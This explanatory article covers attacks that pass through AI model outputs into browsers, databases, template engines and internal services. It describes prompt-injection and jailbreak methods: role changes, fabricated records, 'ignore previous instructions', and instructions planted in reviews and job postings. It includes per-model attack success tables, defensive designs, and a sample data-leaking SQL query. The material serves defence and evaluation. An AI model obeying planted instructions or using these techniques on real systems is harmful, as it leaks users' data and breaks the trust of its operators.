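# Security of AI outputs: preventing, detecting and responding to attacks that exploit AI-generated results

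## How an AI system's output becomes a means of attack

A large language model is an AI system that produces text, including program code and commands, from the text it receives. In a simple chatbot, a person reads the output and decides what to do with it. Many applications pass the output to another system, called the downstream system. For example, a browser displays it as part of a web page, a database runs it as a query, or an operating system executes it as a command. The security of AI outputs concerns attacks that reach a downstream system through the model's text. An attacker who can influence that text can attack the downstream system without connecting to it.

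When a customer asks an online shop's support assistant about a late parcel, the shop's application combines the question with the developer's standing instructions and material it has looked up, perhaps a product page with customer reviews. It sends all this to the model as one block of text, called the prompt. The model returns text that may include an answer, which the application places in a web page. The text may also include a tool call, which is structured output that names a function for the application to run and gives its arguments, such as an order lookup with an order number. The application runs the function, adds the result to the prompt and sends it back to the model to generate more text. A model connected to tools in this way is called an agent.

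By this point, people outside the shop (the customer and the reviewers) have written part of the prompt, and the browser and the order database are acting on the output. No step in the process records whose text influenced which words of the output.

### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. In direct injection, the attacker types the text into the application. In indirect injection, the attacker hides it in material that the model will read later, such as an email or a review, and an innocent user triggers it. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, describes a recruiter's system that asks a model to score each CV against a job's requirements. A candidate adds hidden text telling the model to approve the CV for interview, and the model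 may follow that instruction.

SQL injection is a nearly thirty-year-old flaw in which text from a web form runs as a command in SQL, the language of most databases. Programmers can reliably prevent it with parameterised queries, which send the command and the values to the database separately so that the database engine cannot interpret a value as a command. This works because databases handle commands and values differently. Language models have no such separation, because they receive the developer's rules, the customer's question and a stranger's review as a single sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words) and predict the next token from that sequence.

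Developers can train a model to prioritize their own instructions, or mark outside material with tags, and David C accepts that such measures make attacks harder. But the underlying technology does not distinguish between developers' instructions and outside material, so these measures make a successful injection less likely but still possible. Filters that block known phrases are weaker still, because an attacker can endlessly reword an instruction.

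### Improper output handling

An injected instruction cannot harm a browser or a database until a program acts on the model's response. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes free guidance on software security, defines improper output handling as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's outputs before they pass to other components (*LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*). Because the prompt can control the output, OWASP likens passing it straight to other components to giving users indirect access to additional functions.

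The consequences on OWASP's list are familiar web attacks. The browser attacks are cross-site scripting, where an attacker's script runs inside a page the victim trusts, and cross-site request forgery, where the victim's logged-in browser sends a request the victim never intended. The server attacks are server-side request forgery (making a server send requests to places the attacker cannot reach directly), privilege escalation (gaining rights the attacker's account lacks) and remote code execution (running the attacker's program on someone else's machine). The damage grows if the model has more privileges than its users, or if it processes material where an attacker can plant instructions (indirect injection).

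OWASP separates this from overreliance, which is depending too much on the accuracy of a model's answers. A customer who acts on a chatbot's misstatement of the refund policy has relied on it too much, but an answer that contains a working script is dangerous to display even if every sentence the customer reads is true. Checking only what users type does not help with the script. MITRE's *CWE-1426*, an entry in a standard catalogue of software weaknesses, cites a chat interface that validated its input but not the model's output, which led to cross-site scripting.

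Older documents use the name and number from OWASP's *LLM02*, which gave the same definition under the title "Insecure Output Handling". The 2025 edition of OWASP's list of ten model risks renamed the entry and placed it fifth. The August 2026 edition ranks it tenth but widens its scope. According to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a summary by the security vendor Invicti, the entry now also covers text terminals that interpret control codes in a model's output, and programs that automatically fetch whatever the output links to, which can let attackers steal data through images.

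The fall in rank is weak evidence that the problem has shrunk. OWASP based three-quarters of the ranking on a vote among practitioners and one quarter on 6,639 classified incidents. Advait Patel, a cloud security engineer quoted by ReversingLabs, attributes the drop to the growing urgency of the entries above it. Incident counts also need careful interpretation. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that prompt injection, which practitioners have ranked first for three editions running, would miss the top ten on incidents alone. OWASP's explanation is that teams defend hard against it, so fewer clean exploits reach a public database. That is plausible, but the count would also be low if successful attacks were rare or victims failed to notice them.

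### The confused deputy and its old weaknesses

Security engineers have long called a program in the model's position a confused deputy. The program has legitimate access, and someone without that access gets the program to use it on their behalf. The shop's assistant is allowed to query the order database and a stranger on the internet is not, so the stranger asks the assistant to query it for them.

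*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) recounts a public report of a chatbot that took an order number from the conversation and passed it to a lookup function. The function returned the record without checking who was asking. One of the attacker's messages asked for the contact details on an order, as a customer might. The order numbers followed a predictable pattern, so the attacker could work through them, and the chatbot gave out other customers' email addresses and shipping details.

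Developers can usually fix a confused deputy by making it check whose authority it is using. David C calls a model "inherently confusable" because no such check inside the model is reliable. David C's rule for estimating damage is therefore to assume that the attacker has direct access to every tool the model can call.

The order lookup would have been just as faulty behind an ordinary web form. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude from cases like this that the model usually carries an attack to an existing weakness rather than creating one. They sort these attacks into eight classes, each of which ultimately exploits a classical web flaw.

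| Class | What the model contributes | Where the weakness lies | Basis |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | A database query | The application runs the query with broad database rights | Documented |
| Cross-site scripting | Page code containing a script | The web page displays it without encoding | Documented |
| Server-side template injection | Template expressions | The template engine evaluates them as live code | Documented |
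| Command injection | Arguments for a tool that runs commands | The tool puts them into a system command unchecked | Documented |
| Insecure direct object reference | The identifier of a record | The lookup never checks who may see the record | Documented |
| Cross-site request forgery | Later answers based on a false memory | The assistant's memory store accepts forged requests | Constructed |
| XML external entity injection | A document in XML, a structured data format | The parser opens outside files that the document names | Constructed |
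| Server-side request forgery | A web address | A tool on the server fetches any address | Constructed, then tested |

Earlier research or public reports document five of the classes. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built the other three by analogy and tested one of them, server-side request forgery, in their own application, TicketOracle. The attack's success varied widely between models.

An old type of weakness, such as command injection, can become more dangerous when attackers can reach it through an AI model. The security research group Snyk Labs examined a tool server that runs commands for Amazon's cloud service and contained such a flaw, listed publicly as CVE-2025-5277. These servers often run on a developer's own machine, where an outside attacker cannot connect to them, but the attacker can plant an instruction in a file in a shared code repository. If a developer adds that file to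 a coding assistant's context and then asks for something harmless, such as a list of storage folders, the assistant may include an extra command in its tool call, and the server runs both.

Cross-site request forgery fits the general conclusion less well. A malicious web page makes the user's logged-in browser write a false entry into an assistant's long-term memory, and no prompt injection is needed. The harm comes in a later session, when the model uses the entry and, for example, presents the attacker's payment address as the verified one. The forged request is a classical flaw, but older web applications have no close counterpart to a store of remembered text that shapes an assistant's later advice.

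Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian began from classical web flaws and left out attacks in which the model's output runs as program code, so the attacks they collected were likely to end in classical flaws. Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026), in *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, worked in the opposite direction, starting from all ten of OWASP's 2025 model risks and looking for the nearest entries in MITRE's catalogue. They found at least one entry for every risk except misinformation. A nearest match is weak evidence that a risk is a classical flaw, and one of the entries for prompt injection is specific to models. But the match for improper output handling is close, because one of its two entries is the long-known failure to encode output.

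### A script in DeepSeek's chat page

The cross-site scripting case in the table needs only a chat window and a browser. In 2024 the security researcher Johann Rehberger tried a new model in the web chat of the Chinese company DeepSeek. *DeepSeek AI*, his account on Embrace The Red, reports that he asked for a list of sample scripting attacks, the model supplied it, and one of the samples ran.

A browser displays a web page's ordinary text and acts on its tags, which are marked by angle brackets. DeepSeek's page inserted the model's answer into the page as code, so when one item in the list contained a tag for an embedded frame with a script inside, the browser created the frame and ran the script.

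An attacker gains nothing by running a script in their own browser, so Rehberger looked for a way to bring the text in from outside and found that he could use a document uploaded for analysis. His test file contained an instruction to decode an encoded string and print only the result. Encoding the script mattered because web filters and many models reject an obvious attack. The model decoded the script, the page inserted it, and the browser ran it with the full rights of the chat page, including access to the session token. This stored string proves that the user has logged in, and it was enough by itself to take over the account. Rehberger's script only showed the token on the screen, but it could easily have been changed to send the token elsewhere.

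The model followed an instruction from a file, and no developer can rule that out. The account was in danger because the page treated the model's answer as code. If the page had replaced each opening angle bracket with `&lt;`, the browser would have displayed the bracket instead of starting a tag, and the user would have seen strange but inert text. Rehberger reported the flaw to DeepSeek through the app's general contact form because there was no security channel, and DeepSeek fixed it a day after they exchanged messages.

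Other researchers have since described related behaviour in the same product. N45HT's *Hacking AI with Markdown* reports a script that ran only once the user activated it, a flaw DeepSeek fixed by cleaning the formatted text before display. GCVE's *CVE-2025-26210* (2025) is a disputed record about scripts that run on a domain separate from the chat page, which some third parties regard as intended. Their view has some merit, because a service that lets people try out generated web pages has to run scripts somewhere. Browsers also keep each domain's stored data apart, so a script there could not simply read the chat page's token. The record's severity score of 8.8 out of 10 looks high if that separation holds.

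### Four basic safeguards

Output encoding, the remedy for the DeepSeek flaw, rewrites special characters so that the receiving program treats text as data, not code. The right encoding depends on the receiving program, so OWASP calls for different encoding in web pages and in database queries. Encoding does not help when the application is meant to execute the output, as when a model writes a whole database query, and it does not correct false statements.

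An allow-list is a list of permitted values, and the application refuses everything else. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that an application accept only known identifiers from the model and build the web address itself, so that the model never chooses where a request goes. This blocks unexpected destinations and functions, but not the misuse of a permitted value. In the chatbot case, each order number was valid, and only a check on the requester would have protected the record. The list also has to be in program code, because in the prompt it is more text for the model to process, alongside whatever the attacker has added.

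Least privilege means giving a component only the access its task requires, such as a database account that can read but not delete. David C relays a simple version of this principle from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: a model that processes text from some party should have only that party's privileges. A model reading mail from strangers would then have only the tools its owner would allow a stranger to use. Least privilege limits the damage from a successful injection, but an attacker can still misuse the access that the task requires. For example, an assistant that must read private mail can still leak it.

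In ReversingLabs' article, Larry Maccherone, founder of Lumenize, objects that restricting agents also limits their ability to find and repair security gaps, and that nobody can approve an agent's behaviour in advance if the agent generates it anew on each run. The second objection applies to approving actions one by one, but is weaker against limiting what a credential can access, because that limit works without predicting what the agent will do.

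A sandbox is an isolated environment that limits what running code can reach, which makes it suitable for applications that must execute model-written code. It confines the effects of mistakes and attacks unless the code escapes, which sometimes happens. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a well-known escape in which a template expression starts from an empty string and moves through Python's internal object hierarchy to reach a function that runs system commands. Even without escaping, code in a sandbox can leak private data if it has access to both the data and an open network connection. For this reason, the sandboxing that OWASP advises, as Infosecurity Magazine summarises it, also restricts access to the network and internal services.

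## Database queries and program code written by a model

Output encoding does not help when a database has to run the model's text as a query, as happens behind many chatbots that answer questions about an organisation's data. Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023) carried out the first study of prompt-to-SQL injection, their term for attacks on these chatbots, in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*. Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues extended the work to real applications in *Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications*, written for the software engineering conference ICSE 2025.

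### From a question to a query

The test application was a job marketplace with a chatbot. Its database had a table of job postings and a table of users, with their email addresses and phone numbers. Pedro and colleagues built the chatbot with LangChain, a popular framework for connecting models to other software.

When a user asks for the five best-paid jobs in London, LangChain fills in a prompt template. The template includes an instruction to act as an expert in PostgreSQL, a common database system. It also lists the tables and columns, and has fields for the question, query, result and answer. The model writes the query, and LangChain stops it there because it would otherwise invent a result. LangChain then runs the query, adds the returned rows to the prompt and sends everything back to the model, which writes the answer.

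LangChain calls this design an SQL chain. It allows one query per question, while LangChain's SQL agent lets the model run several before answering. Both run queries with the rights of the chatbot's database account. The researchers gave that account permission to read and change every table, so the model was the only safeguard.

### Attacks through the chat

With LangChain's default template, the chatbot deleted the users table, changed another person's phone number and listed everyone's contact details when an attacker asked it to. Each attack succeeded in all 20 trials. The attacker did not need to know SQL, because the model translated plain English into a query.

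Pedro and colleagues then added rules to the prompt, including one that allowed only SELECT statements, which read data. A direct instruction to ignore the rules and delete the table failed, but a longer message succeeded every time. It gave the model a new role and included a fabricated record in which the same command had already run.

Another rule restricted the model to returning the logged-in user's data. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, the model wrote a query for rows whose user number was both 1 and 2, so the database returned nothing. When the attacker claimed to be user 2, the model dropped the restriction. The application had identified the logged-in user and put the correct number in the prompt, but the attacker could contradict it because the model received it only as text.

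### Attacks through a stored record

An attacker can also reach the database without using the chat. Anyone could post a job on the test site, and the model read the job descriptions when other users asked about them. The researchers posted a job description containing an instruction to answer that there were no jobs. The SQL chain gave this false answer in every trial, and the SQL agent gave it in 60% of trials. In its other trials, the agent left out the planted posting or listed it with the rest.

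A more serious attack worked only on the agent because it needed more than one query. When a user asked for the job descriptions, the planted text made the model replace a victim's email address with the attacker's, which could let the attacker take over the account through password recovery. The model then reran the original query and gave a normal-looking answer that omitted the malicious posting. The attack also succeeded in every trial. A ban on changing data would prevent the account takeover but not the false answer, which requires only a legitimate read query.

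### How widely the attacks worked

The attacks also worked on LlamaIndex, a framework whose query-writing component closely resembles LangChain's. Pedro and colleagues tried seven models: GPT-3.5, GPT-4, PaLM 2, Llama 2, Vicuna, Guanaco and Tulu. Guanaco and Tulu were too unreliable to run as agents, and Tulu was also too unreliable for the false-answer test. Every attack worked on every model on which it could be tested, although PaLM 2 and Llama 2 only partly completed the account takeover. They changed the email address, but then revealed the attack in the answer or kept repeating the change. The researchers attribute this to the models' difficulty with complex instructions, not to the models detecting the attack.

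Two hired security analysts then attacked local copies of five open-source applications, with up to three hours each per application. They tried to bypass a ban on writing to the database, produce a false answer and inject a multi-step query. They succeeded in 22 of the 23 possible combinations of application, model and attack.

The researchers also trained a small model to write attack prompts and gave it 40 attempts per combination. It succeeded in 11 of the 23 combinations.

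| Model behind the application | Analysts' successes | Automated tool's successes |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 | 10 of 11 | 9 of 11 |
| GPT-4 | 12 of 12 | 2 of 12 |

GPT-4's greater resistance therefore stopped most of the automated attacks but none of the analysts' attacks.

Restrictions in the applications' own code were more reliable. Dataherald blocked queries that change data, so the attacks that needed to modify the database were impossible whatever query the model wrote. Na2SQL ran only one query per question, which ruled out the multi-step attack. The attack that produced a false answer still worked against both applications.

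In a later article, *Words Become SQL*, Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) acknowledge that public reports of attackers deleting customer databases this way remain rare. They suggest that this is because disclosure is limited and these systems are new. The tests on real applications show that the weakness is common in this kind of software, but they cannot show how often criminals exploit it.

### Defences and their costs

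The two versions of the study tested five defences between them.

| Defence | How it works | What it stopped | Added time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Database permissions | The chatbot's account can read data but not change it | Deletions and changes, including the account takeover | Negligible |
| Query checking | A program lets only SELECT statements through | Deletions and changes, including the account takeover | 0.7 ms |
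| Query rewriting | A program narrows each query to the user's own rows | Reading other users' data | 1.87 ms |
| Preloading | The application puts the user's own data in the prompt, so the model needs no query for it | Reading other users' data | 0.7 ms |
| Model guard | A second model looks for planted instructions in the returned rows | The false answer and the account takeover | About 0.43 s |

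The 0.7 ms for preloading comes from the 2023 version, but the ICSE version gives the same figure for query checking instead, so it is only a rough estimate. Either way, these checks take a tiny fraction of the 1.6 to 5.2 seconds that the chatbot needed to answer a question in the 2023 tests. Preloading also makes the prompt longer, which takes more time and money to process, and large amounts of data may not fit.

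Query rewriting takes the model's query and puts a narrower one inside it. If user 5 gets the model to ask for every email address in the users table, the program changes the query to:

```
SELECT email FROM (
  SELECT * FROM users WHERE user_id = 5
) AS users_alias
```

The database first runs the inner query, which returns only user 5's row. The outer query, which the attacker influenced, can select only from that row. The developer specifies in advance which tables are sensitive and what condition applies to each, so the restriction does not depend on the model.

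The model guard was the only defence that stopped the false answer. In the final test, it caught 99.55% of 1,120 malicious prompts, missing about five. It raised no false alarms on 150 harmless results, but with a sample of that size, the true false positive rate could still be as high as about 2%. The test was also fairly easy, because a model had generated many of the malicious prompts by rewording the analysts' prompts, and none of the analysts had designed theirs to defeat the guard. In 2023, Pedro and colleagues called the guard a partial mitigation because a model that reads an attacker's text is itself vulnerable to prompt injection.

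The guard is also by far the slowest defence. Pedro and colleagues report an average of 0.43 seconds per check, but their total of 64.15 seconds for 60 malicious prompts works out to about 1.07 seconds each. A chatbot user might tolerate either delay.

### What newer models change

The attacks in the study are now harder to repeat. In April 2026, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried similar techniques on newer models without success, and found that telling a model to ignore its previous instructions no longer worked reliably. However, their application fetched web addresses and did not write SQL. They also did not try to improve the prompts, whereas a determined attacker would look for new attacks.

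Pedro and colleagues could not reproduce the account takeover on GPT-4 in the 2023 version of their study, but they succeeded in the ICSE version. By 2025 they regarded the resistance of stronger models as "incidental rather than a dependable mitigation".

Making a model more resistant to injection does not change the database account's permissions. If the account can read every customer's record, any successful injection can expose all of them, and so can a mistake in which the model leaves out a filtering condition. Many harmful queries also look ordinary. A model can learn to refuse to delete a table, but a request for one customer's address may be legitimate or an attack, depending on who sent it. The application can check the sender from the login, whereas the model has only the text in its prompt.

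### One hostile query under three accounts

Suppose a shop keeps 10,000 customers in one table, with one row for each. Customer 5 logs in and manipulates the shop's assistant into writing this query:

```
SELECT name, email FROM customers
```

The damage depends on the account that the assistant uses to connect to the database.

| Assistant's database account | Rows returned | Other customers' rows leaked | Result of a command to delete every row |
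|---|---|---|---|
| Full access | 10,000 | 9,999 | The database deletes all 10,000 |
| Read-only | 10,000 | 9,999 | The database refuses |
| Read-only, limited to customer 5's rows | 1 | 0 | The database refuses |

Making the account read-only prevents changes to the data but does not keep it confidential. Stopping the leak also requires the database to limit which rows the account can read.

Ordinary table permissions are too coarse for this, because they allow or forbid access to a whole table. One solution is a view, a stored query that behaves like a table. The shop can define a view that contains only the current customer's row, and give the assistant's account access to the view but not the table behind it. Some databases can also filter the rows for each user with a rule attached to the table itself.

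The customer number in the view or rule must come from the login session, and the model's query must not be able to change it. For example, if the application stores the number in a PostgreSQL session setting, a SELECT statement can call a function that changes the setting, so the application needs to block that function or keep the number somewhere the query cannot alter.

Row limits are less useful for an assistant that serves the shop's sales manager, who may need figures from every customer. A database view can instead leave out names and contact details, or provide only totals, so that a manipulated query exposes less.

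### Why parameterised queries help little

Parameterised queries rely on the programmer writing the command. When a model writes the whole query, an attacker can influence the command itself. Sending the query through the same database functions does not prevent this, because the database has no fixed command to keep separate from the values.

OSV's *CVE-2025-67510* (2025), a vulnerability record published in December 2025, describes a flaw in Neuron, a PHP framework for building agents. The framework's tool for changing data used functions meant for parameterised queries, but it accepted any SQL its caller supplied, so a prompt injection could make it delete tables. The record rates the flaw's severity 9.4 out of 10. The tool had to allow some changes to data, but it should not have let text from an agent choose any change at all.

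Pedro and colleagues recommend that developers use parameterised queries or purpose-built functions instead of letting the model write SQL. The programmer writes a fixed set of queries, such as "find an order by its number", and the model chooses one and fills in the values. The database can then separate command from value again. The customer number should still come from the login session. Attackers can also still misuse values they have planted, so some designs check where each value came from. The main drawback is that the assistant can answer only the questions the programmer foresaw.

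If users need to ask open-ended questions, the application can parse each query before running it. The parser turns the query into a tree that shows its commands, tables, columns and functions, and the application compares these with an allow-list. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend combining this check with a read-only account and a ban on destructive operations.

Searching a query for forbidden words is a poor substitute for limiting the database account's permissions. Neuron had a tool meant to be read-only, which checked that each query began with a permitted word such as SELECT and contained no forbidden words. MITRE's *CVE-2025-67509* (2025) explains that the tool let through SELECT statements that can write files to the database server. An attacker could exploit this only if the account had permission to write files and the server allowed writing to a useful place, such as a folder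 that a website serves to visitors. Neuron's developers fixed the tool in version 2.8.12.

### Applications that run model-written code

Some applications run code that a model writes, which can give an attacker far more freedom than a database query. *Generative AI Models* (2024) describes a web application for solving difficult mathematics problems. A user types a problem in ordinary language, the model writes a program to solve it, and the application runs the program and returns the result. An attacker could phrase the input so that the model writes a program that encrypts a connected database or returns its contents.

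JFrog, a software security company, found that prompt injection could lead to remote code execution in Vanna.AI, a database assistant that turns questions into SQL (CVE-2024-5565). Restricting the database account would not be enough to protect a tool like this, because the attacker's code runs outside the database.

Early frameworks often contained such flaws. In *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, Liu, Deng and colleagues (2024) built LLMSmith, a tool that searches the frameworks' source code for paths from a user's input, through the model, to functions that execute code. The researchers then tested those paths with prompts. They found 20 vulnerabilities in 11 frameworks, and 11 of the vulnerabilities received CVE identifiers. These figures describe the software at that time, much of which has since changed.

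Between January 2023 and October 2024, public reports described at least 529 vulnerabilities in 75 prominent projects for building and running language models. That total includes flaws in everything from model training to user interfaces, so it does not show how many arose because software failed to validate a model's output. *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* (2026) presents a smaller dataset of 116 vulnerabilities, but it also combines flaws that have a model "in the loop" with flaws in the wider software ecosystem.

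The 2026 work cites an advisory about vLLM, a program that runs models for other applications. vLLM's parser for tool calls written by the model Qwen3-Coder allowed remote code execution. The parser reads a tool call before any tool receives it, so a check inside the tool would have run too late to prevent this.

### Templates that run by mistake

An application can also run a model's output as code when its developer meant only to display text. In *Make Agent Defeat Agent*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) looked for taint-style vulnerabilities, in which untrusted input reaches a sensitive operation. The vulnerabilities they found in agents have received 23 CVE identifiers. One example involves Jinja2, a template engine for Python.

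A template engine builds a page from fixed text with marked places for changing values, such as "Dear {{ name }}". The engine evaluates whatever is between the double braces as an expression. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian explain that the vulnerable agent passed the model's whole response to Jinja2 as the template. The attacker told the model to include an expression in its response, and the engine evaluated it, which led to the sandbox escape described earlier.

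The developer could have avoided this by writing a fixed template and passing the response to it as a value. Jinja2 would then insert any braces in the response as ordinary characters without evaluating them. A fixed template protects the server just as a parameterised query protects a database. If the result is a web page, the application still has to encode the response for the browser.

### Isolating code that has to run

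A fixed template can't help the mathematics application, which exists to run new programs. It needs a sandbox, which can be very strict because each program only receives a problem and returns a result, without needing a database connection, passwords or network access. The application can start a fresh sandbox for each request, limit its time and memory, and delete it afterwards, so that one user's program cannot leave anything behind for the next. A malicious program might still return a wrong answer or waste its allotted computing time, but it could not encrypt a database or return customer records unless it escaped from the sandbox.

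## Requests to internal services: the TicketOracle experiment

A program that solves mathematics problems can run without a network connection, but many assistants need one to look up prices or read web pages. An attacker who can choose the address an assistant fetches can use the assistant's server to reach internal systems that outsiders cannot access directly.

This is server-side request forgery (SSRF), a flaw much older than language models. MDN's *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)*, a reference page for web developers, gives the example of a website that fetches an image from any address a visitor supplies. A visitor can enter the address of an administrative page on the company's internal network. The visitor's computer cannot reach that page, but the server can, and it sends the contents back.

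Attackers often target the server itself. Every computer can connect to its own services through the loopback address, 127.0.0.1, or localhost. These local services often require no authentication (OWASP, 2024). OWASP's *A10:2021* (2021) adds another target, the metadata services that most cloud providers run at a fixed internal address. A machine can query such a service for its configuration and, in some setups, for access credentials.

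In an application built on a model, the address for a request can be an argument in a tool call. *Silent Egress* (2026), a study of agents that leak data through web requests, argues that this makes SSRF more powerful, because an attacker can describe a goal in plain language without knowing the tool's parameters. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian used TicketOracle to test a simpler version in which the attacker always supplied the complete address.

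### A concert assistant with one tool

TicketOracle is a test website that lists concert dates, ticket prices and reviews, and has a chat assistant that answers questions about them. When a user asks what a Metallica ticket costs, for example, the model writes a tool call containing the web address of the event's record, and the application fetches the record. The assistant has only this tool, which accepts any address.

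An administrative service on the same machine as the assistant's tool holds user records and can create or delete users and events. It accepts connections only through the loopback address, so nobody outside the machine can reach it directly, and it relies on this instead of checking who sent each request. It therefore accepts requests from the tool.

The attacker in the experiment has no login and can only write to the assistant and post reviews. However, administrative pages tend to have predictable names, so the attacker can guess their addresses.

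| Attack | What the attacker wants the assistant to do | Evidence of success |
|---|---|---|
| Port probing | Try a numbered port on the server to find out whether a service is listening | The assistant's reply |
| Data disclosure | Fetch the user records | The assistant's reply |
| State change | Fetch an address that deletes a user or an event | The assistant's reply |
| Blind state change | Fetch an address that changes data but returns an empty response | The server's audit log |
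| Planted review | Obey an instruction in a review when an innocent user asks about the event | The assistant's reply |

In April 2026, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian ran these attacks against seven models. For each model and attack, they made ten consecutive attempts in a single conversation. They then gave the assistant stricter written instructions and tried again.

### Results

The table shows the number of successful attacks out of ten.

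| Model | Port probing | Data disclosure | State change | Blind state change | Planted review | Planted review, stricter instructions |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
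| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2 resisted every attack, while every attack made through the chat succeeded against Llama. The application had the same vulnerability whichever model it used, so anyone who deployed it with Claude might have concluded that it was safe, and then exposed the administrative service by switching to a cheaper model.

A model's resistance to one attack poorly predicted its resistance to another. Gemini and GPT-oss always carried out the visible state change but never carried out the blind one, although both kinds of request alter the server's data.

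The scoring may also have missed some successful requests. Except in the blind attack, a trial counted as a success only if the assistant both fetched the address and repeated the result to the user, so a model that fetched the user records but left them out of its answer scored zero. This doesn't affect Claude, which never made the request. But nearly every direct attack succeeded against Qwen and DeepSeek, and their zeros for the planted review could include fetches that never appeared in their answers. Checking the server's log for all five attacks would have revealed any such fetches.

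### A rule in the prompt and a rule in code

The stricter instructions contained an allow-list of address patterns and event identifiers, and told the model to refuse anything else. They stopped all four direct attacks on all seven models. With the planted review, successful attacks fell from five to none on GPT-oss but rose from six to ten on Llama.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the stricter instructions blocked the attack on one model and amplified it on another. The Llama result is weaker evidence than it looks because the researchers also changed the review. For the stricter version, they added a false notice that the internal address had joined the allow-list, which may have made the review more persuasive to Llama regardless of its instructions. The samples are also small. Fisher's exact test, a standard method for comparing small groups, shows that if both versions were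 equally vulnerable and every trial were independent, a gap as wide as Llama's would arise by chance about 9% of the time. For GPT-oss the figure is about 3%.

The Llama result does show that a written allow-list can fail completely. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian write that the list catches forbidden addresses before the model's reasoning can act on them, but the list was part of the prompt, and only the model applied it. In all ten trials, Llama followed the reviewer's claim about the list instead of the list itself. An attacker whose direct requests fail could therefore post such a review, ask the assistant about the concert and receive the user records in the answer.

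If the fetching function itself holds the list, it blocks the same attack. Llama still reads the review and writes a tool call with the internal address, but the function doesn't find that address in its list and returns an error. The review can change the tool call but not the list, because the function never reads the review. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend this kind of check, though they tested only the written version.

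### How many clean trials a security test needs

The zero success rates for Claude and GPT-5.2 are encouraging, but ten trials are too few to show that an attack rarely works. If an attack succeeds with probability *p* on each independent trial, the chance of no successes in *n* trials is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. An attack that works 26% of the time has about a 5% chance of failing ten times in a row, so ten failures rule out only success rates above about 26%, at 95% confidence.

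| Clean independent trials | Highest success rate still plausible at 95% confidence |
|---|---|
| 10 | 26% |
| 29 | 10% |
| 59 | 5% |
| 299 | 1% |
| 2,995 | 0.1% |

A useful shortcut is to divide three by the number of trials, which works well above about 30.

The trials in TicketOracle were not independent, so even the 26% is too optimistic. The model received the whole conversation each time, including its earlier answers. Claude's refusals of port probing shrank from long explanations to almost single words. A model that has refused or complied once may be more likely to do the same again.

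*What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove* (Kaur, 2026) gives a standard correction for trials that come in related groups, which divides the number of trials by 1 + (*m* − 1)*ρ*, where *m* is the group size and *ρ* is the correlation within each group. With ten trials in a conversation and a correlation of only 0.1, the divisor is 1.9, so the ten trials carry roughly as much information as five independent ones. If the first answer fully determined the rest, the ten would count as one trial, which excludes only rates above 95%. The correlation can't be estimated from a single conversation per attack.

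Adding up a model's results across attacks doesn't solve the problem. If all the attacks were equally likely to work, Claude's 40 clean trials in the four direct attacks would exclude attack success rates above about 7%, but Gemini's scores of zero and ten show how much attacks can differ.

The zeros have some value because the same attacks worked on other models. Kaur recommends a positive control, a system already known to have the weakness, to show that a test can detect it. Llama is the positive control here. Without it, the zeros could mean that the attacks were badly written.

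A better test would start a new conversation for each trial, vary the wording and record every request the server makes. Researchers would also need to repeat it for each new model. Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 had already superseded the models in the experiment by the end of July 2026.

### Better models or better design

Some developers expect better models to remove most of the danger, and recent results give them good reason. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model trained to find attacks so that OpenAI can fix weaknesses before release, and reports that the company's latest models have already saturated common robustness tests. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes results from a prompt injection benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan, in which attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 0.2% of cases with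 one attempt and 2.0% within 15 attempts. The rates for its predecessor, Opus 4.8, were 0.5% and 5.5%.

The opposing view is that application design has to contain the problem. Tech Times' *AI Agent Security Hits Its Reckoning* (2026) reports that in June 2026 OWASP, like David C, traced the weakness to how language models read text. Schneier on Security takes a position between the two, arguing that prompt injection can't be prevented in general but that developers are getting much better at blocking it in specific cases.

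The main difficulty for the optimistic view is that a result in one setting may not carry over to another. Claude Opus 4.6 was one of the two models that resisted every attack in TicketOracle. Anthropic tested it against an attacker that adapts to the model's responses. In coding tasks, the attacker failed even with 200 attempts. When the model operated a computer through its screen, with extended reasoning but no added safeguards, the attacker succeeded 17.8% of the time with one attempt and 78.6% within 200. Anthropic expects lower rates in real use, because the test used a strong attacker and made the planted text easy to find. But it warns that testing with fixed sets of known attacks can give "a false sense of security", and TicketOracle repeated a fixed prompt.

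Results also vary between developers. On the Gray Swan benchmark, attackers beat the strongest version of GPT-5.6 within 15 attempts in 20% of cases. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark of office tasks, reports successful attacks on leading models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon. PromptArmor sells security services and stands to gain from such findings, but they fit the general pattern.

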